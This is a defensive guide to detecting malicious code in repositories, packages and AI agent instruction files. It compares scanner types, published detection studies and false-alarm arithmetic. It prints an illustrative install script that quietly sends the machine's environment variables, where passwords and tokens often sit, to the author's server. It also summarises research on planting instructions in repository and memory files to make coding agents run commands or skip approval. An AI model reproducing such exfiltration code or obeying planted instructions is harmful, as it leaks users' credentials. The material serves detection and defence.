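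The user's request also affects the risk. In *Beyond the Payload* (2026), attacks through repository files succeeded most often, and agents warned the user least often, when the user asked the agent to run the project's tests. This held for all four combinations of agent and model, although Codex was the most vulnerable and Claude Code with Sonnet 4.6 the least. Test requests are probably riskier because running tests already means running commands from the repository, so one more doesn't stand out. Backslash found a similar weakness in Codex's unattended mode, which follows AGENTS.md before it starts the user's task and doesn't ask for approval.

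However, not every malicious instruction works. *Security Impact of Coding Agent's Memory Files* (Santos de Moura and Güler, 2026) tested three agent-model combinations with memory files that presented removing security checks as good practice or demanded it outright. Across 36 programming tasks, the share of secure results changed by between −8 and +6 percentage points, with no consistent pattern. The study is small, but it suggests that making an agent write less secure code may be harder than making it run a command. It also found that agents could flag a file as an attack and still produce vulnerable code, so a warning from the agent doesn't mean its code is safe.

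The simplest precaution is to read these files in a plain text viewer, with invisible characters showing, before running any agent in the folder. Asking an agent in that folder whether the instructions are safe is not a safe way to check them, because the agent may load them before it answers.

### The inventory

Honest projects can show most of the signs below, so each is a reason to look further, not a verdict.

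| Place | Warning sign | First check |
|---|---|---|
| Install and build scripts | A script or `binding.gyp` in a package with nothing to compile | Read every command that runs on installation, build or import |
| Encoded text and large files | Code that decodes text and runs it, or a huge file in an odd folder | Sort a full local copy by file size and ask what each large file is for |
| Unicode characters | Invisible or direction-changing characters in code, or names that mix alphabets | List every such character with its file and line |
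| Release files | A version with no matching tag, or files missing from the source | Compare the release with the tagged source or an official build |
| Package names | A near-copy of a known name, or a name that only a model suggested | Find the publisher and the package's first release date |
| CI workflows | Encoded commands, unknown addresses or unneeded permissions | Read each workflow and see who last changed it |
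| Editor and agent settings | A command that runs on opening, or a web address nobody chose | Read the dot folders before opening the project, and again after each update |
| Agent instruction files | Orders to hide something, skip approval or install an unrelated package | Read them in a plain text viewer that shows invisible characters |

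## Run the scanners in order, and know what each one does

A scanner can search the places where deceptive code can be hidden in a repository faster than a person can, but each kind checks only some of those places and looks for different signs. It makes sense to start with the quick, safe checks and leave the one that runs the repository's code until last.

### Six steps for an unknown repository

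1. Get the files without installing them. Use a virtual machine (a simulated computer that you can delete afterwards) with no passwords or tokens on it. Download the source from GitHub and the release from the registry as two archives, and unpack them as ordinary files. Python's `pip download` command isn't a safe shortcut, because it can run a package's build script to find out what else the package needs. Keep editors and coding agents away from them, as when making the inventory. Record each archive's hash, a short code that changes if anyone alters the file.

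2. Compare the release with the source. A standard comparison tool lists the files that appear on only one side and the lines that differ in the others. The normal build process explains some differences. Put the rest at the top of the list for the later steps. The xz build script would have been on that list.

3. Run the rule-based scans on both copies. These include the search for invisible characters and the checks on the package's name and publisher. Look at each scanner's exclusions first. A repository can contain a `.semgrepignore` file, or comments, that make the code scanner Semgrep skip parts of the code, and some scanners skip very large files by default.

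4. Run a model-based scan. Start with whatever the earlier steps flagged and the files that run during installation, build or import. Use a model that can't run commands, since the files may contain instructions meant for an agent. Ask what data the code handles, where the data goes and whether the package's stated purpose requires that, and only then ask for a verdict.

5. Run the package in isolation if there is still doubt. Put fake credentials on the virtual machine, cut it off from the office network, and record the programs it starts, the files it changes and the addresses it tries to contact. Skip this step if an earlier one has already given a good reason to reject the package.

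6. Record the decision. Write down the hashes, the scanners with their versions and settings, each alert and the reason for dismissing it, and who decided. The decision covers only that version of the package.

Every alert needs an explanation, even if a later scan comes back clean. For example, if the release contains a build script that the source lacks, a language model's opinion that the script looks fine doesn't explain how the script got into the release.

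### How each kind of scanner reaches a verdict

| Kind of scanner | What it examines | What raises an alert |
|---|---|---|
| Pattern rules | The text or structure of the code | A match with a pattern that somebody has written |
| Metadata signals | Name, publisher, dates, downloads | A near-copy of a popular name, or a publisher with no history |
| Source-to-release comparison | Two copies of the project | A file or line in the release that doesn't come from the source |
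| Data-flow and call-graph analysis | Routes through the code | A route from private data to the network, for example |
| Sandboxed execution | What happens when the code runs | An unexpected connection, file change or program |
| Trained classifier | Measurements of the package | A resemblance to known malicious packages |
| Language model | The code and the text around it | A judgment that the behaviour is harmful |

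YARA rules look for particular text or bytes in any file. Semgrep works out the structure of the code first, so one rule can match a function call however the programmer has laid it out. *LLM-Enhanced Hierarchical Heterogeneous Graph Representation Learning for Malicious Python Package Detection* (Gao, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes a YARA check from Warehouse, the software that runs Python's main public package registry, PyPI. The check examines only `setup.py`, a package's install script, and flags commands that start other programs or contact the network.

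Metadata checks need information from outside the package. For example, to detect a package whose name is a misspelling of a popular one, the scanner needs a list of popular packages to check the name against.

A call graph shows which functions call which others. Data-flow analysis follows a piece of data through the code, such as from a password file to a function that sends it over the network. Both can connect steps that an attacker has spread over several files.

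A sandbox scanner runs code and records what it does, so it can catch malicious behavior that the source code disguises. HERCULE, for example, installs packages in isolated containers and monitors their requests to the operating system. But a malicious package may delay its attack, or do nothing if it finds signs of a test machine. Benign packages also do a lot during installation, which can cause false alarms. *Bridging Expert Reasoning and LLM Detection* (Guo, Song and colleagues, 2026) tested Packj, which traces npm packages as they run. Packj caught 96.4% of the malicious packages, but its precision implies that it also flagged about 65% of the benign ones.

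A trained classifier turns each package into a list of measurements, such as which functions the package calls and how random its names look. An attacker can change some of these measurements without changing what the code does. Guo and colleagues also tested scanners on packages with scrambled names and encoded text. The best version of the MalGuard classifier fell from 94.8% accuracy on ordinary packages to 85.4% on these. GuardDog, which relies on rules, stayed at about 88%.

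Language models can compare what the code does with what the package is for, as human analysts tend to do. Guo and colleagues extracted 7,889 explanations from security companies' reports, and 58% were based on behaviour that contradicted the package's purpose, such as a charting library that gives an outsider remote control of the machine. Their tool, IntelGuard, gives a language model similar past cases with the analysts' reasoning, and it was 96.5% accurate on the scrambled packages. Without those cases, GPT-4o-mini missed 85% of the scrambled malicious packages, and GPT-4o flagged 62% of the scrambled benign ones. Readable names, which an attacker can choose, evidently have a large influence on a model's verdict.

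### One install script, three scanners

Suppose the shop's developer finds this `setup.py` in a Python version of the delivery calculator:

```python
import os, platform
from setuptools import setup
from delivery.stats import report

# Count installs so we know which systems to support
report({"system": platform.system(), "settings": dict(os.environ)})

setup(name="delivery-calc", version="1.2.0", packages=["delivery"])
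```

The function `report`, in another file, sends whatever it receives to the author's server. `os.environ` contains the machine's environment variables, where developers often keep passwords and access tokens. The script still looks harmless because many projects collect installation statistics.

A pattern rule like the one in Warehouse would not flag the script, because the rule only checks `setup.py` for a command that contacts the network, and that command is in the other file. Extending the rule to every file would catch the command but also flag packages that contact a server for legitimate reasons.

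A data-flow scanner can start at the command that sends the data and work backwards. It can trace the data to the input of `report`, then to `setup.py`, which reads it from `os.environ`. The scanner can therefore report that installing the package sends the machine's environment variables to an outside server. This is much more useful than a match on a network command because it identifies what data is sent and when. Someone still has to write a rule that flags this route, and a rule covering all system information would also flag a project that sends only the name of the operating system.

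A language model may detect that counting operating systems doesn't require the `settings` item, which is the mismatch between comment and code that a careful human reader would look for. The model could also accept the comment and pass the script, or flag it merely because an install script contacts a server. To test why the model flagged the script, a reviewer can delete the `settings` item and ask again in a new session. If the model still flags the script as malicious, its first verdict probably had little to do with the passwords.

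### Vulnerability scanners look for mistakes

Vulnerability scanners look for mistakes that an attacker could exploit. Some compare the versions of a project's dependencies with a database of published flaws. Others search the code for known types of mistake, such as putting user input straight into a database command. Malware scanners look for code written to do harm.

The script above could pass both kinds of vulnerability scan. A new package has no entry in the database, and the code contains no mistake, since it does what its author wanted. A repository with a "no known vulnerabilities" badge may therefore still be malicious. OWASP's benchmark measures how well a tool finds mistakes, so it doesn't help a buyer judge how well the tool finds malicious code.

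OSV, a vulnerability database that Google's open-source security team maintains, also lists confirmed malicious packages. Guo and colleagues used it to find the malicious packages for their study. A dependency scan that includes those entries can catch a malicious release once somebody has reported it, but doesn't protect anyone who installs the release before then.

The shop needs both kinds of scanner, since an honest project can be full of mistakes that a malware scanner would ignore.

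### The same scanners in three tests

Gao and colleagues compared older scanners with their own detector, H²GLM. It represents a package as a graph of its files and functions and uses a language model to label what each function does. On their test set, H²GLM caught 98.7% of the malicious packages with a precision of 95.6%, while HERCULE caught 91.0% with a precision of 87.6%.

To build that test set, they collected 3,049 malicious Python packages from an existing benchmark and public security reports, removed duplicates and near-duplicates, and used 2,134 of them for testing. They chose benign packages from the most popular ones on PyPI and matched them to the malicious ones by file size. Matching by size was sensible because malicious packages tend to be small, and a detector could otherwise score well by flagging small packages. But popular packages are a poor substitute for the obscure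 ones that a developer most needs to check. H²GLM was also trained on packages from the same collection, an advantage that HERCULE and the rule-based scanners didn't have.

Most of the published scores are consistent with a test set containing equal numbers of malicious and benign packages. But the precision and recall of OSSGadget, a Microsoft scanner, would give an accuracy of about 55% on such a set, while the paper reports 64%. The scores for MPHunter, another graph-based tool, have a similar but smaller discrepancy.

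The study by Guo and colleagues and *MALTOTAL* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested some of the same older scanners on Python packages, also with roughly equal numbers of malicious and benign ones. This section covers *MALTOTAL*'s own scanner later.

| Scanner | Gao: precision / recall | Guo: precision / recall | Zhao: precision / recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| Warehouse check | 92.6% / 46.0% | 51.7% / 99.3% | Not tested |
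| OSSGadget | 53.1% / 91.6% | 51.1% / 87.9% | 48.9% / 9.0% |
| GuardDog | Not tested | 91.5% / 82.2% | 92.4% / 92.9% |
| Bandit4Mal | 39.1% / 22.0% | 34.6% / 47.9% | 38.8% / 18.6% |

In one test, Warehouse missed more than half of the malicious packages but rarely flagged a benign one. In the other, it caught nearly all of them but, judging by its precision, also flagged about 93% of the benign packages. The researchers may have run it on different files or counted its alerts differently, but the papers don't give enough detail to tell. OSSGadget's recall ranged from 9.0% to 91.6%.

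GuardDog is the only scanner in the table that did well in more than one test, so it's a reasonable choice for the rule-based step. Bandit4Mal, adapted from a tool that looks for mistakes in Python code, did badly in all three tests. For the others, a published score is weak evidence of how they will perform in a different setup. It would be better to try a scanner on a few known malicious packages and a few ordinary ones before relying on it.

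Package size also affects detection. Qwen3-14B, the best of the language models that Gao and colleagues tested without extra tools, caught 91.5% of malicious packages with less than 5 KB of Python code, but only 57.7% of larger ones. They attribute the drop to cutting off text that didn't fit in the model's input.

Gao and colleagues also ran H²GLM on more than 20,000 new PyPI packages over four months. They reported 32 packages to PyPI's security team, which confirmed and removed 19. Most scanners are never tested this way. However, the paper doesn't say how many packages H²GLM flagged before the researchers chose which to report.

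### Language models are better at verdicts than explanations

*An Evaluation of Large Language Models for Detection of Malicious Python Packages* (Ryan, Khalil and colleagues, 2026) tested 13 language models on two tasks, deciding whether a package was malicious and naming its malicious behaviours from a list of 47 types in seven categories. Twelve of the models were publicly downloadable, and the other was GPT-4.1, from 2025. The researchers tried five ways of prompting and up to three settings for how random the answers were.

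On the first task, the models usually caught the malicious packages but often flagged safe ones too. Recall fell below 50% in 1.6% of the combinations of model, prompt and setting, while precision fell below 50% in 51% of them. The average F1 ranged from 0.40 for the weakest model to 0.99 for GPT-4.1.

The prompt made a surprisingly large difference. A plain request gave an average F1 of 0.74. Adding worked examples, which often helps language models, cut it to 0.23, barely better than flagging every package. With one prompting method, Qwen-3 Coder scored 0 at the least random setting and 1 at the most random.

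Those swings look less strange given how small the test was. Ryan and colleagues collected 4,070 packages, but to save money they used one file from each of 103 packages for the first task. Of these packages, 93 were benign, none with more than 260 lines. Only ten were malicious, so one extra miss lowers recall by ten percentage points. Four models got a perfect score in at least one combination, but with so few malicious files and up to 15 combinations per model, some of those scores may be luck.

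The second task used all 370 malicious packages in the collection, so its results are more solid. The models did worse on it:

| What the model had to do | F1 |
|---|---|
| Name the right categories of behaviour | 0.69 |
| Name the specific behaviours | 0.48 |

The second figure reflects a recall of 41% and a precision of 70%. About 92% of the answers contained at least one correct behaviour, but only 0.3% named exactly the right set. An exact match is a harsh standard, since a package often had eight or nine behaviours. Longer packages were harder, and the choice of prompt or settings made little difference.

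The models were best at detecting behaviours that are visible in a few lines of code. They missed 29% of the commands passed to the operating system, but 97% of the package names that imitated a real one by adding or changing a word. The metadata check is meant to catch those names.

The false reports had a different cause. Models often mistook ordinary code in `setup.py` for an attack during installation, and the download of a safe program for a download of malware. For the delivery calculator, a model could correctly call the package malicious but blame the standard `setup()` line.

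Some of the apparent errors came from the labels. In one package, the label referred to disabled attack code, while the model identified the command that would run. The true scores are therefore probably a little higher than published.

Ryan and colleagues recommend using language models to pick out packages for a person to examine, but not to explain what a package does. I think a model's explanation is still useful if it points to a specific line, because a reader can check that line. A wrong explanation alone is not a reason to clear the package, because the model's verdict may still be right.

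### MalTotal: cut the code down, then ask a model

Zhao, Wang and colleagues designed MalTotal to make model-based scanning cheap enough for very large numbers of repositories. It works in three stages:

1. Find the sensitive calls. MalTotal has a list of 2,147 built-in functions in Python, JavaScript, Java, Go and PHP that run code, use the network, handle files, read sensitive data or encrypt and encode. A language model identifies functions in outside libraries that do the same things. Semgrep then searches for all of them, and MalTotal drops any file that uses none.
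2. Cut out the code around each call. A program works backwards from the call to the code that supplies its data or decides whether it runs, going up to three function calls deep. It then merges pieces that largely overlap.
3. Judge each piece. The language model DeepSeek-V3 identifies the sensitive operations, traces the data, assesses the intent and gives a verdict.

In the delivery calculator, the second stage should put the sending command and the line that reads `os.environ` in the same piece, even though they are in different files.

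On 2,168 repositories, this cut the model's fees from $86.25 to $5.19 and the average time per repository from 252 seconds to 140. The model's recall on Python packages was also higher, at 96.9%, compared with 91.2% when it received whole suspicious files instead of pieces. A scan of about 120,000 repositories cost $338, or roughly 0.3 cents each. These figures leave out the powerful server that did the other work and the time people spent checking alerts.

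| Language | Malicious samples | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| Python | 3,188 | 95.7% | 96.9% |
| JavaScript | 3,438 | 93.3% | 88.9% |
| PHP | 143 | 98.5% | 90.2% |
| Java | 75 | 97.1% | 88.0% |
| Go | 80 | 95.9% | 87.5% |

The paper's text gives the JavaScript precision as 89.0%, which doesn't match its table. The PHP, Java and Go results are less certain because the samples are small. The malicious samples came from an earlier search for malware source code on GitHub, and the benign ones from projects with many stars. Openly published malware may be easier to recognise than code disguised as a delivery calculator.

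The scan of 120,000 repositories is a more realistic test, although they came from a list of projects with suspicious popularity and so aren't typical of GitHub. MalTotal flagged 1,553 of them, and security researchers reviewed every one:

| Result of the review | Repositories | Share of alerts |
|---|---|---|
| Confirmed malicious | 564 | 36% |
| Openly labelled as security research, testing or malware collections | 487 | 31% |
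| False positives | 502 | 32% |

The middle group contains code that could do harm but isn't deceptive, because its authors disclose what it can do. Only about one alert in three was useful for finding hidden malice. The paper also counts 200 C and C++ projects among the confirmed cases, but MalTotal doesn't support either language, and the paper doesn't explain how it found them. Nobody reviewed the repositories that MalTotal passed, so its recall in this scan is unknown.

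Most of the false positives were legitimate tools that behave suspiciously, such as remote administration programs and system monitors that run commands. The code alone may not be enough to judge these cases, so a reviewer has to ask whether the tool's users know what it does.

Zhao and colleagues found two main reasons why MalTotal missed malicious packages. In some packages, the harmful code was in a dependency, which MalTotal doesn't check for malice. In another case, the visible code only started PowerShell, a Windows command tool, which ran a separate script containing the attack. They considered a stricter prompt, but expected it to flag more legitimate programs that start scripts the same way. They also warn that comments in the code could cause the model to label harmful code as safe.

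### Scanners for agent instructions

There seems to be no published independent test of scanners on AGENTS.md or CLAUDE.md files. The closest evidence concerns skills, which *Scan Before You Install* (2026) defines as packages of written instructions, scripts and reference files that an agent loads when a task needs them. Like agent instruction files, skills can direct an agent in ordinary prose.

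Two papers tested skill scanners on labelled examples. *The Devil Wears Markdown* (2026) used 80 malicious skills and 60 benign ones. *MaliciousSkillBench* (2026) used a larger collection.

| Test | Scanner | Malicious skills caught | Benign skills flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| *The Devil Wears Markdown* | Cisco Skill Scanner | 91% | 55% |
| *The Devil Wears Markdown* | Cisco, with a small language model | 85% | 67% |
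| *MaliciousSkillBench* | Cisco, running locally | 2.5% | 1.1% |
| *MaliciousSkillBench* | SkillFortify | 25.3% | 49.9% |
| *MaliciousSkillBench* | SkillSpector, fixed rules only | 0% | 0.6% |

None of these results justifies relying on a scanner alone. SkillFortify flagged benign skills about twice as often as malicious ones. Cisco's scanner caught nearly all of the malicious skills in one paper and almost none in the other. The papers used different settings and different skills, so users can't tell which result to expect. Adding the language model made Cisco's scanner worse on both measures, but that model, Qwen3-8B, is far smaller than the leading ones.

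Scanners also disagree on real skills. *After the Party* (2026) compared three scanners on 61,990 listings in a public registry, and they disagreed on 23,702 of them (38%). *ClawHub Security Signals* (2026) reports that 81.9% of flagged skills were flagged by only one of three scanners. VirusTotal, a service that checks files for malware, flagged 72.8% of the skills that the registry labeled malicious, and SkillSpector flagged 6.8%. The registry's labels aren't reliable ground truth, so these percentages don't measure recall. For this reason, *Context Matters* (2026) treats scanner results as alerts, not as proof that a skill is malicious.

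The scanner makers' own figures also need careful reading. Snyk, which sells security tools, examined 3,984 public skills in February 2026 and reported security flaws in 1,467 of them, or 36.8%. According to *SkillTester* (2026), Snyk's staff confirmed malicious code by hand in 76 cases, fewer than 2% of the skills. The larger number includes accidental flaws as well as malicious code, and neither number measures how many malicious skills the scanner missed.

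For an instruction file, a person with a plain text viewer is still the better check.

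## Set the alarm threshold and estimate the false alarms

Many scanner tests use about as many malicious packages as benign ones, but in practice nearly all packages are benign, so even a low false positive rate can produce more false alarms than true ones. A team can estimate the number of true and false alarms before deploying a scanner.

### From a false positive rate to a working day

Precision, the share of alarms that are correct, depends on the recall *r*, the false positive rate *f* and the base rate *b*, which is the share of all examined packages that are malicious. A share *b* × *r* of all packages is malicious and flagged, and a share (1 − *b*) × *f* is benign and flagged. Therefore:

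precision = (b × r) / (b × r + (1 − b) × f)

Suppose 1 package in 1,000 is malicious and the scanner catches 90% of those. Out of 100,000 packages, 100 are malicious and the scanner flags 90 of them. The table shows how many of the other 99,900 the scanner wrongly flags at two false positive rates, and the resulting workload if 2,500 packages arrive each day.

| | Rate of 0.1% | Rate of 10% |
|---|---|---|
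| True alarms per 100,000 packages | 90 | 90 |
| False alarms per 100,000 packages | 100 | 9,990 |
| Precision | 47% | 0.9% |
| Alarms per day | 4.7 | 252 |
| Checking time per day, at 1 minute an alarm | 5 minutes | 4.2 hours |
| Checking time per day, at 10 minutes an alarm | 48 minutes | 42 hours |

About half the alarms are true when the false positive rate equals the recall times the base rate, which is 0.09% in this example.

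Precision depends as much on the share of packages that are malicious as on the scanner. With 90% recall and a false positive rate of 0.1%, precision is 90% if 1 package in 100 is malicious, but only 8% if 1 in 10,000 is. Precision measured in a balanced test therefore doesn't carry over to real use. In the test by Guo and colleagues, GuardDog's precision of 91.5% implies a false positive rate of about 7.6%. At that rate, its precision would be about 1% if 1 package in 1,000 were malicious.

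Estimates of the base rate vary with what people count. Ryan and colleagues estimate that PyPI has about 73 benign packages for each malicious one. They compared all the malicious packages in a public collection with all the projects on PyPI, so the figure includes malware that PyPI removed long ago. Anyone scanning new uploads needs the rate among those uploads, which is lower.

### What PyPI's maintainers would accept

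PyPI introduced its own malware checks in 2020 and turned them off two years later. Vu, Newman and Meyers (2022) studied why in *A Benchmark Comparison of Python Malware Detection Approaches*, a preprint of the paper published as *Bad Snakes* (2023). They interviewed two people from PyPI's maintainer community and one academic. The sample is small, but fewer than ten people were directly involved in scanning PyPI for malware.

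PyPI received about 20,000 releases a week and removed about 20 malicious packages, a base rate of 1 in 1,000. An administrator was willing to spend about 20 minutes a week on malware reports, at about a minute each, so the true reports alone took up all of that time. A scanner with a false positive rate of 0.1% would have added about 20 false alarms a week and doubled the work.

The maintainers considered even a false-alarm rate of 0.01% too high, although that is only two false alarms a week. Vu and colleagues set the limit for a check that runs after publication at 0.001%, or one false alarm every five weeks. This is stricter than the time budget requires, but the maintainers saw little benefit in catching more malware. Many malicious packages had almost no real downloads, and the maintainers believed that a skilled attacker could always get past an automated check. They were willing to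 miss other attacks if the scanner caught the frequent, crude ones.

The scanners of the time were far from meeting these limits. Vu and colleagues ran three of them on 168 malicious packages and 986 randomly chosen benign ones, first on the install script `setup.py` alone and then on every Python file. The table shows the share of packages with at least one alert.

| Scanner | Malicious, `setup.py` only | Benign, `setup.py` only | Malicious, all files | Benign, all files |
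|---|---|---|---|---|
| PyPI's own checks | 58.9% | 14.9% | 85.7% | 67.8% |
| OSS Detect Backdoor | 50.6% | 33.1% | 85.1% | 77.2% |
| Bandit4Mal | 66.7% | 70.2% | 90.5% | 84.6% |

The lowest false positive rate, 14.9%, would have meant about 3,000 false alarms a week, or 50 hours of checking at a minute each. Bandit4Mal flagged benign install scripts more often than malicious ones. The gap between the two ways of running PyPI's checks may also explain why Gao and colleagues and Guo and colleagues later got such different results with the checks.

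Requiring several alerts before raising an alarm didn't solve the problem. No malicious package set off more than three alerts from PyPI's checks on `setup.py`, while one benign package set off 45. A threshold of four would have missed every malicious package and still flagged some benign ones.

PyPI came to rely on outside researchers, who run their own scanners, sort through the false alarms and report what they find. It processed more than 2,000 malware reports in 2025 and handled 66% of them within four hours (PyPI, 2025). Socket, which sells package-security tools, reports that over 95% of the issues PyPI resolved within a day took under a minute to handle. But a researcher has usually gathered the evidence before PyPI receives a report. A raw scanner alarm takes longer, so ten minutes per alarm is a safer assumption for a team that has to investigate alarms itself.

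### One detector at five thresholds

Many scanners score each package and raise an alarm when the score passes a threshold. Lowering the threshold catches more malicious packages but also flags more benign ones. In *One Detector Fits All*, Montaruli, Compagna and colleagues (2025) measured this trade-off with a trained classifier on 91,949 releases they collected from PyPI over 37 days in spring 2025.

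| Maximum false positive rate | Malicious found | Malicious missed | False alarms | Precision | Alarms per day |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 30% | 208 | 8 | 27,478 | 0.75% | 748 |
| 10% | 196 | 20 | 9,152 | 2.1% | 253 |
| 1% | 180 | 36 | 781 | 18.7% | 26 |
| 0.1% | 92 | 124 | 81 | 53.2% | 4.7 |
| 0.05% | 77 | 139 | 35 | 68.8% | 3.0 |

The researchers chose 0.1% for PyPI's maintainers. At that setting the detector found about 2.5 malicious packages a day and raised about 2.2 false alarms, a large improvement over the scanners of 2022. But it missed 124 of the 216 known malicious packages, a recall of 43%. Precision was slightly above the 47% in the worked example because malicious packages were more common in this stream, at about 1 in 425.

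Even 43% may be too high. The researchers took their labels from public databases of malicious packages and their own review of the detector's alarms, so a malicious package that nobody noticed would count as benign.

Checking all the detector's alarms, true and false, takes about 33 minutes a week, which is more than the 20 minutes the maintainers have. Montaruli and colleagues conclude that the detector fits within the 20 minutes, but they count only the false alarms, which take about 15.

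The number of false alarms per extra catch is a better guide to the threshold than precision. Moving from 0.1% to 1% finds 88 more malicious packages and adds 700 false alarms, or about eight per extra catch. Moving from 1% to 10% finds only 16 more, with over 500 false alarms for each. The next step, to 30%, adds about 1,500 per extra catch. If each alarm takes a minute to check, one extra catch takes about nine minutes in the first step, almost nine hours in the second and 25 hours in the third. The 1% setting is probably better than the 0.1% setting for anybody who can spare 26 minutes a day.

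A threshold tuned on a test collection may also perform worse on new packages. With the false positive rate held at 1%, an earlier version of the detector caught about 95% of the malicious packages in a standard collection but only 69% in 80 days of live uploads. Adding those uploads to its training data helped it catch 83% in later uploads. GuardDog caught most of the malicious packages in other studies, where its false positive rate was not fixed, but only 6.6% of those in the standard collection when held to 1%.

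### Why a company can choose a more sensitive setting

Montaruli and colleagues also tried the detector on a large software company's 584 Python dependencies, which published 1,596 releases in the same 37 days. They chose the 10% setting because it had caught 91% of the known malicious packages on PyPI.

A 10% false-alarm rate would have produced about 160 false alarms. They saw 46, or 1.24 a day, a rate of 2.9%. The 10% rate therefore describes PyPI's stream, not the company's. One likely reason is that the benign training examples from live uploads were well-ranked packages, which probably resemble a company's dependencies more than they resemble the average new upload.

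No attack hit any of the 584 dependencies during the trial, so all 46 alarms were false, precision was zero, and recall can't be calculated. The setting is still reasonable, because reviewing them at ten minutes each takes less than eight hours over five weeks, which is probably far less work than cleaning up after one stolen password. Reviewing the alarms for all of PyPI at the same setting would take 42 hours a day.

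The company examined about 43 releases a day, compared with PyPI's 2,500. It had more to lose from each miss because it was already using these packages, whereas many malicious uploads to PyPI reach hardly anyone. A false alarm also does less damage at a company, where it delays an upgrade, than on PyPI, where it could get an honest author's work removed.

A team can find its own threshold by running the scanner on the packages it installed or upgraded in the past few months. It should count the alarms at several settings and choose the most sensitive one whose alarms somebody will have time to check.

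### How to read a maker's accuracy claim

Datadog, which sells monitoring and security software, uses a language model to scan its own pull requests, nearly 10,000 a week. *Detecting malicious pull requests at scale with LLMs* (Lamb, Hamsen and colleagues) reports a false positive rate of 0.03%, accuracy above 99.3% and balanced accuracy above 93.5%.

Accuracy, the share of verdicts that are correct, is a poor measure when attacks are rare. If 1 change in 1,000 is malicious, a scanner that never raises an alarm is 99.9% accurate.

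Balanced accuracy is the average of recall and the share of benign changes that the scanner passes, so attacks count as much as benign changes even when they are rare. With a false positive rate of 0.03%, the scanner passes 99.97% of benign changes, so a balanced accuracy of 93.5% implies a recall of 2 × 93.5 − 99.97, or about 87%. At that recall, the scanner could have missed about one malicious change in eight. The published figures are minimums, so the real result may have been better, and the scanner did catch every commit in a set of known attacks on npm packages.

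That calculation assumes all three figures come from the same changes, which is doubtful. The article lists them together under a curated dataset and says the accuracy figure comes from "hundreds of PRs" (pull requests). Hundreds of cases are too few to establish a rate of 3 in 10,000, because a single false alarm in 700 benign changes would be 0.14%, nearly five times the published rate.

Seeing no false alarms wouldn't be enough either. If the true false-alarm rate is *p*, the chance of seeing none in *n* independent benign cases is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. This falls to 5% when *p* is about 3/*n*, so a test with no false alarms is compatible with any rate up to roughly 3/*n*. A maker needs about 10,000 benign changes without a false alarm to support a claim that the rate is at most 0.03%.

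Datadog may well have enough cases, because its security staff spent several months classifying every alarm from the live system as true or false. At nearly 10,000 pull requests a week, they would have reached the necessary number almost immediately. The article doesn't say whether the 0.03% comes from this trial. If it does, the live figure covers only false alarms, because nobody routinely examines the changes a scanner passes. Recall would still come from the curated set, which includes attacks that people and language models wrote for it. Lamb and colleagues also used known false alarms to revise the model's instructions, so a fair test needs changes they didn't use for those revisions.

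At 0.03%, the scanner would raise about three false alarms a week, which is still a manageable load. If one pull request a week were malicious, roughly one alarm in four or five would be true.

*From single pull requests to full software packages*, a later article by Doutre, Peronnet and colleagues, describes a second stage that investigates whatever the first stage flags. On 690 diffs, it cut the false positives from 17 to 0 and raised accuracy from 97.4% to 99.86%, which leaves one wrong verdict. Zero false positives in 690 diffs is still compatible with a true rate of about 0.4%, or some 40 false alarms a week at Datadog. The article also reports that the system detected 95.5% of confirmed malicious packages. That figure is for whole packages rather than diffs, and the article describes the matching false positive rate only as low.

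By the same reasoning, the perfect scores in the small test by Ryan and colleagues are compatible with a false positive rate of about 3%. If 1 package in 1,000 is malicious, about 97% of the alarms could then be false.

### Alarms per file and per repository

A false positive rate also depends on whether it is counted per file or per repository. Suppose a scanner's maker reports no false alarms in 5,000 files. The true rate could still be 3 in 5,000, or 0.06% per file. At that rate, the chance that every file in a 2,000-file repository passes is 0.9994²⁰⁰⁰, or about 30%, so the scanner would raise at least one false alarm in about 70% of such repositories. If the true rate were 0.01% per file, which is also consistent with the test result, the figure would be 18%.

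This assumes that the files are independent, which they usually aren't. Files in one project share authors, habits and copied code, so false alarms tend to cluster. As a result, more repositories have no false alarms, but the rest have a great many. In the study by Vu and colleagues, OSS Detect Backdoor produced 124,267 alerts on one benign package. The only reliable way to measure the rate per repository is to scan whole repositories and count how many raise an alarm.

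The chance of a false alarm also grows with the size of a diff. Datadog's first scanner splits a long diff into chunks and flags the whole diff if it flags any chunk. This is sensible because an attacker may hide one bad line in a huge update. But if each chunk had a 0.03% chance of a false alarm, a diff of 7 chunks would have a 0.2% chance and one of 500 chunks would have a 14% chance, again assuming independence.

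The choice of unit also affects counts of attacks. Montaruli and colleagues traced the 92 malicious packages that their detector found at the 0.1% setting to 22 campaigns, each made up of packages with the same or nearly the same code.

### Triage that keeps the true alarms

When a scanner raises more alarms than people can check, a team can raise the threshold or triage the alarms. Triage means sorting them so that people spend their time on the ones most likely to matter. Each measure below saves work but can hide an attack if a team applies it too broadly.

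A team can save work by grouping alarms that have the same cause. PyPI's *Inbound Malware Volume Report* (2023) notes that several researchers may report the same package separately, and that administrators respond to the duplicates too. Grouping by campaign would also have saved work in Montaruli and colleagues' study. But the flagged code has to match, because a team that groups alarms merely by the rule that raised them may dismiss an attack along with a hundred harmless packages.

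The team should reuse earlier verdicts on identical files. Doutre and colleagues store each package's verdict under the package's hash, and when a package changes they scan only the new code. Reusing verdicts also repeats any mistakes in them, so the team should discard old verdicts whenever it improves the scanner. The reviewer should still be able to open the whole package, since one new line can activate code that was already there.

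A sensitive filter that uses little compute can run before a check that uses more. The second stage checks only what the filter flags, so an attack gets through if either stage misses it. If each stage catches 95% of the attacks that reach it, the two together catch about 90%. Datadog's filter initially accepted web addresses that imitated the company's own because it couldn't look them up. The team fixed this by adding an ordinary program that compares every address with a list of likely imitations.

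Exceptions should be narrow. Lamb and colleagues reduced false alarms partly by excluding patterns they considered safe, such as demonstration environments and certain tests. An attacker who learns of such an exclusion can put code there, and the xz attackers hid theirs in what looked like test data. It is safer to tie each exception to one rule and the hash of one file, so that the alarm returns if anyone changes the file. The scanner should also log the alarms it suppresses.

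It is better to sort the queue by the kind of evidence than by the number of alerts. Vu and colleagues found that network access in an install script was a relatively good sign of malice, whereas starting another program was about as common in benign packages as in malicious ones. They suggest combining signals, since suspicious code in a package with a suspicious name is stronger evidence than either alone. Alarms lower in the queue can wait, but they shouldn't be closed automatically.

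A flagged package should be held until someone has reviewed the alarm. PyPI (2024) has a quarantine status for suspicious projects and planned to apply it automatically after "enough credible reports", though it was still working out what would count as enough. A company can do something similar by staying on its current version until somebody has checked the new one. Upgrades that fix a serious vulnerability should be checked first.

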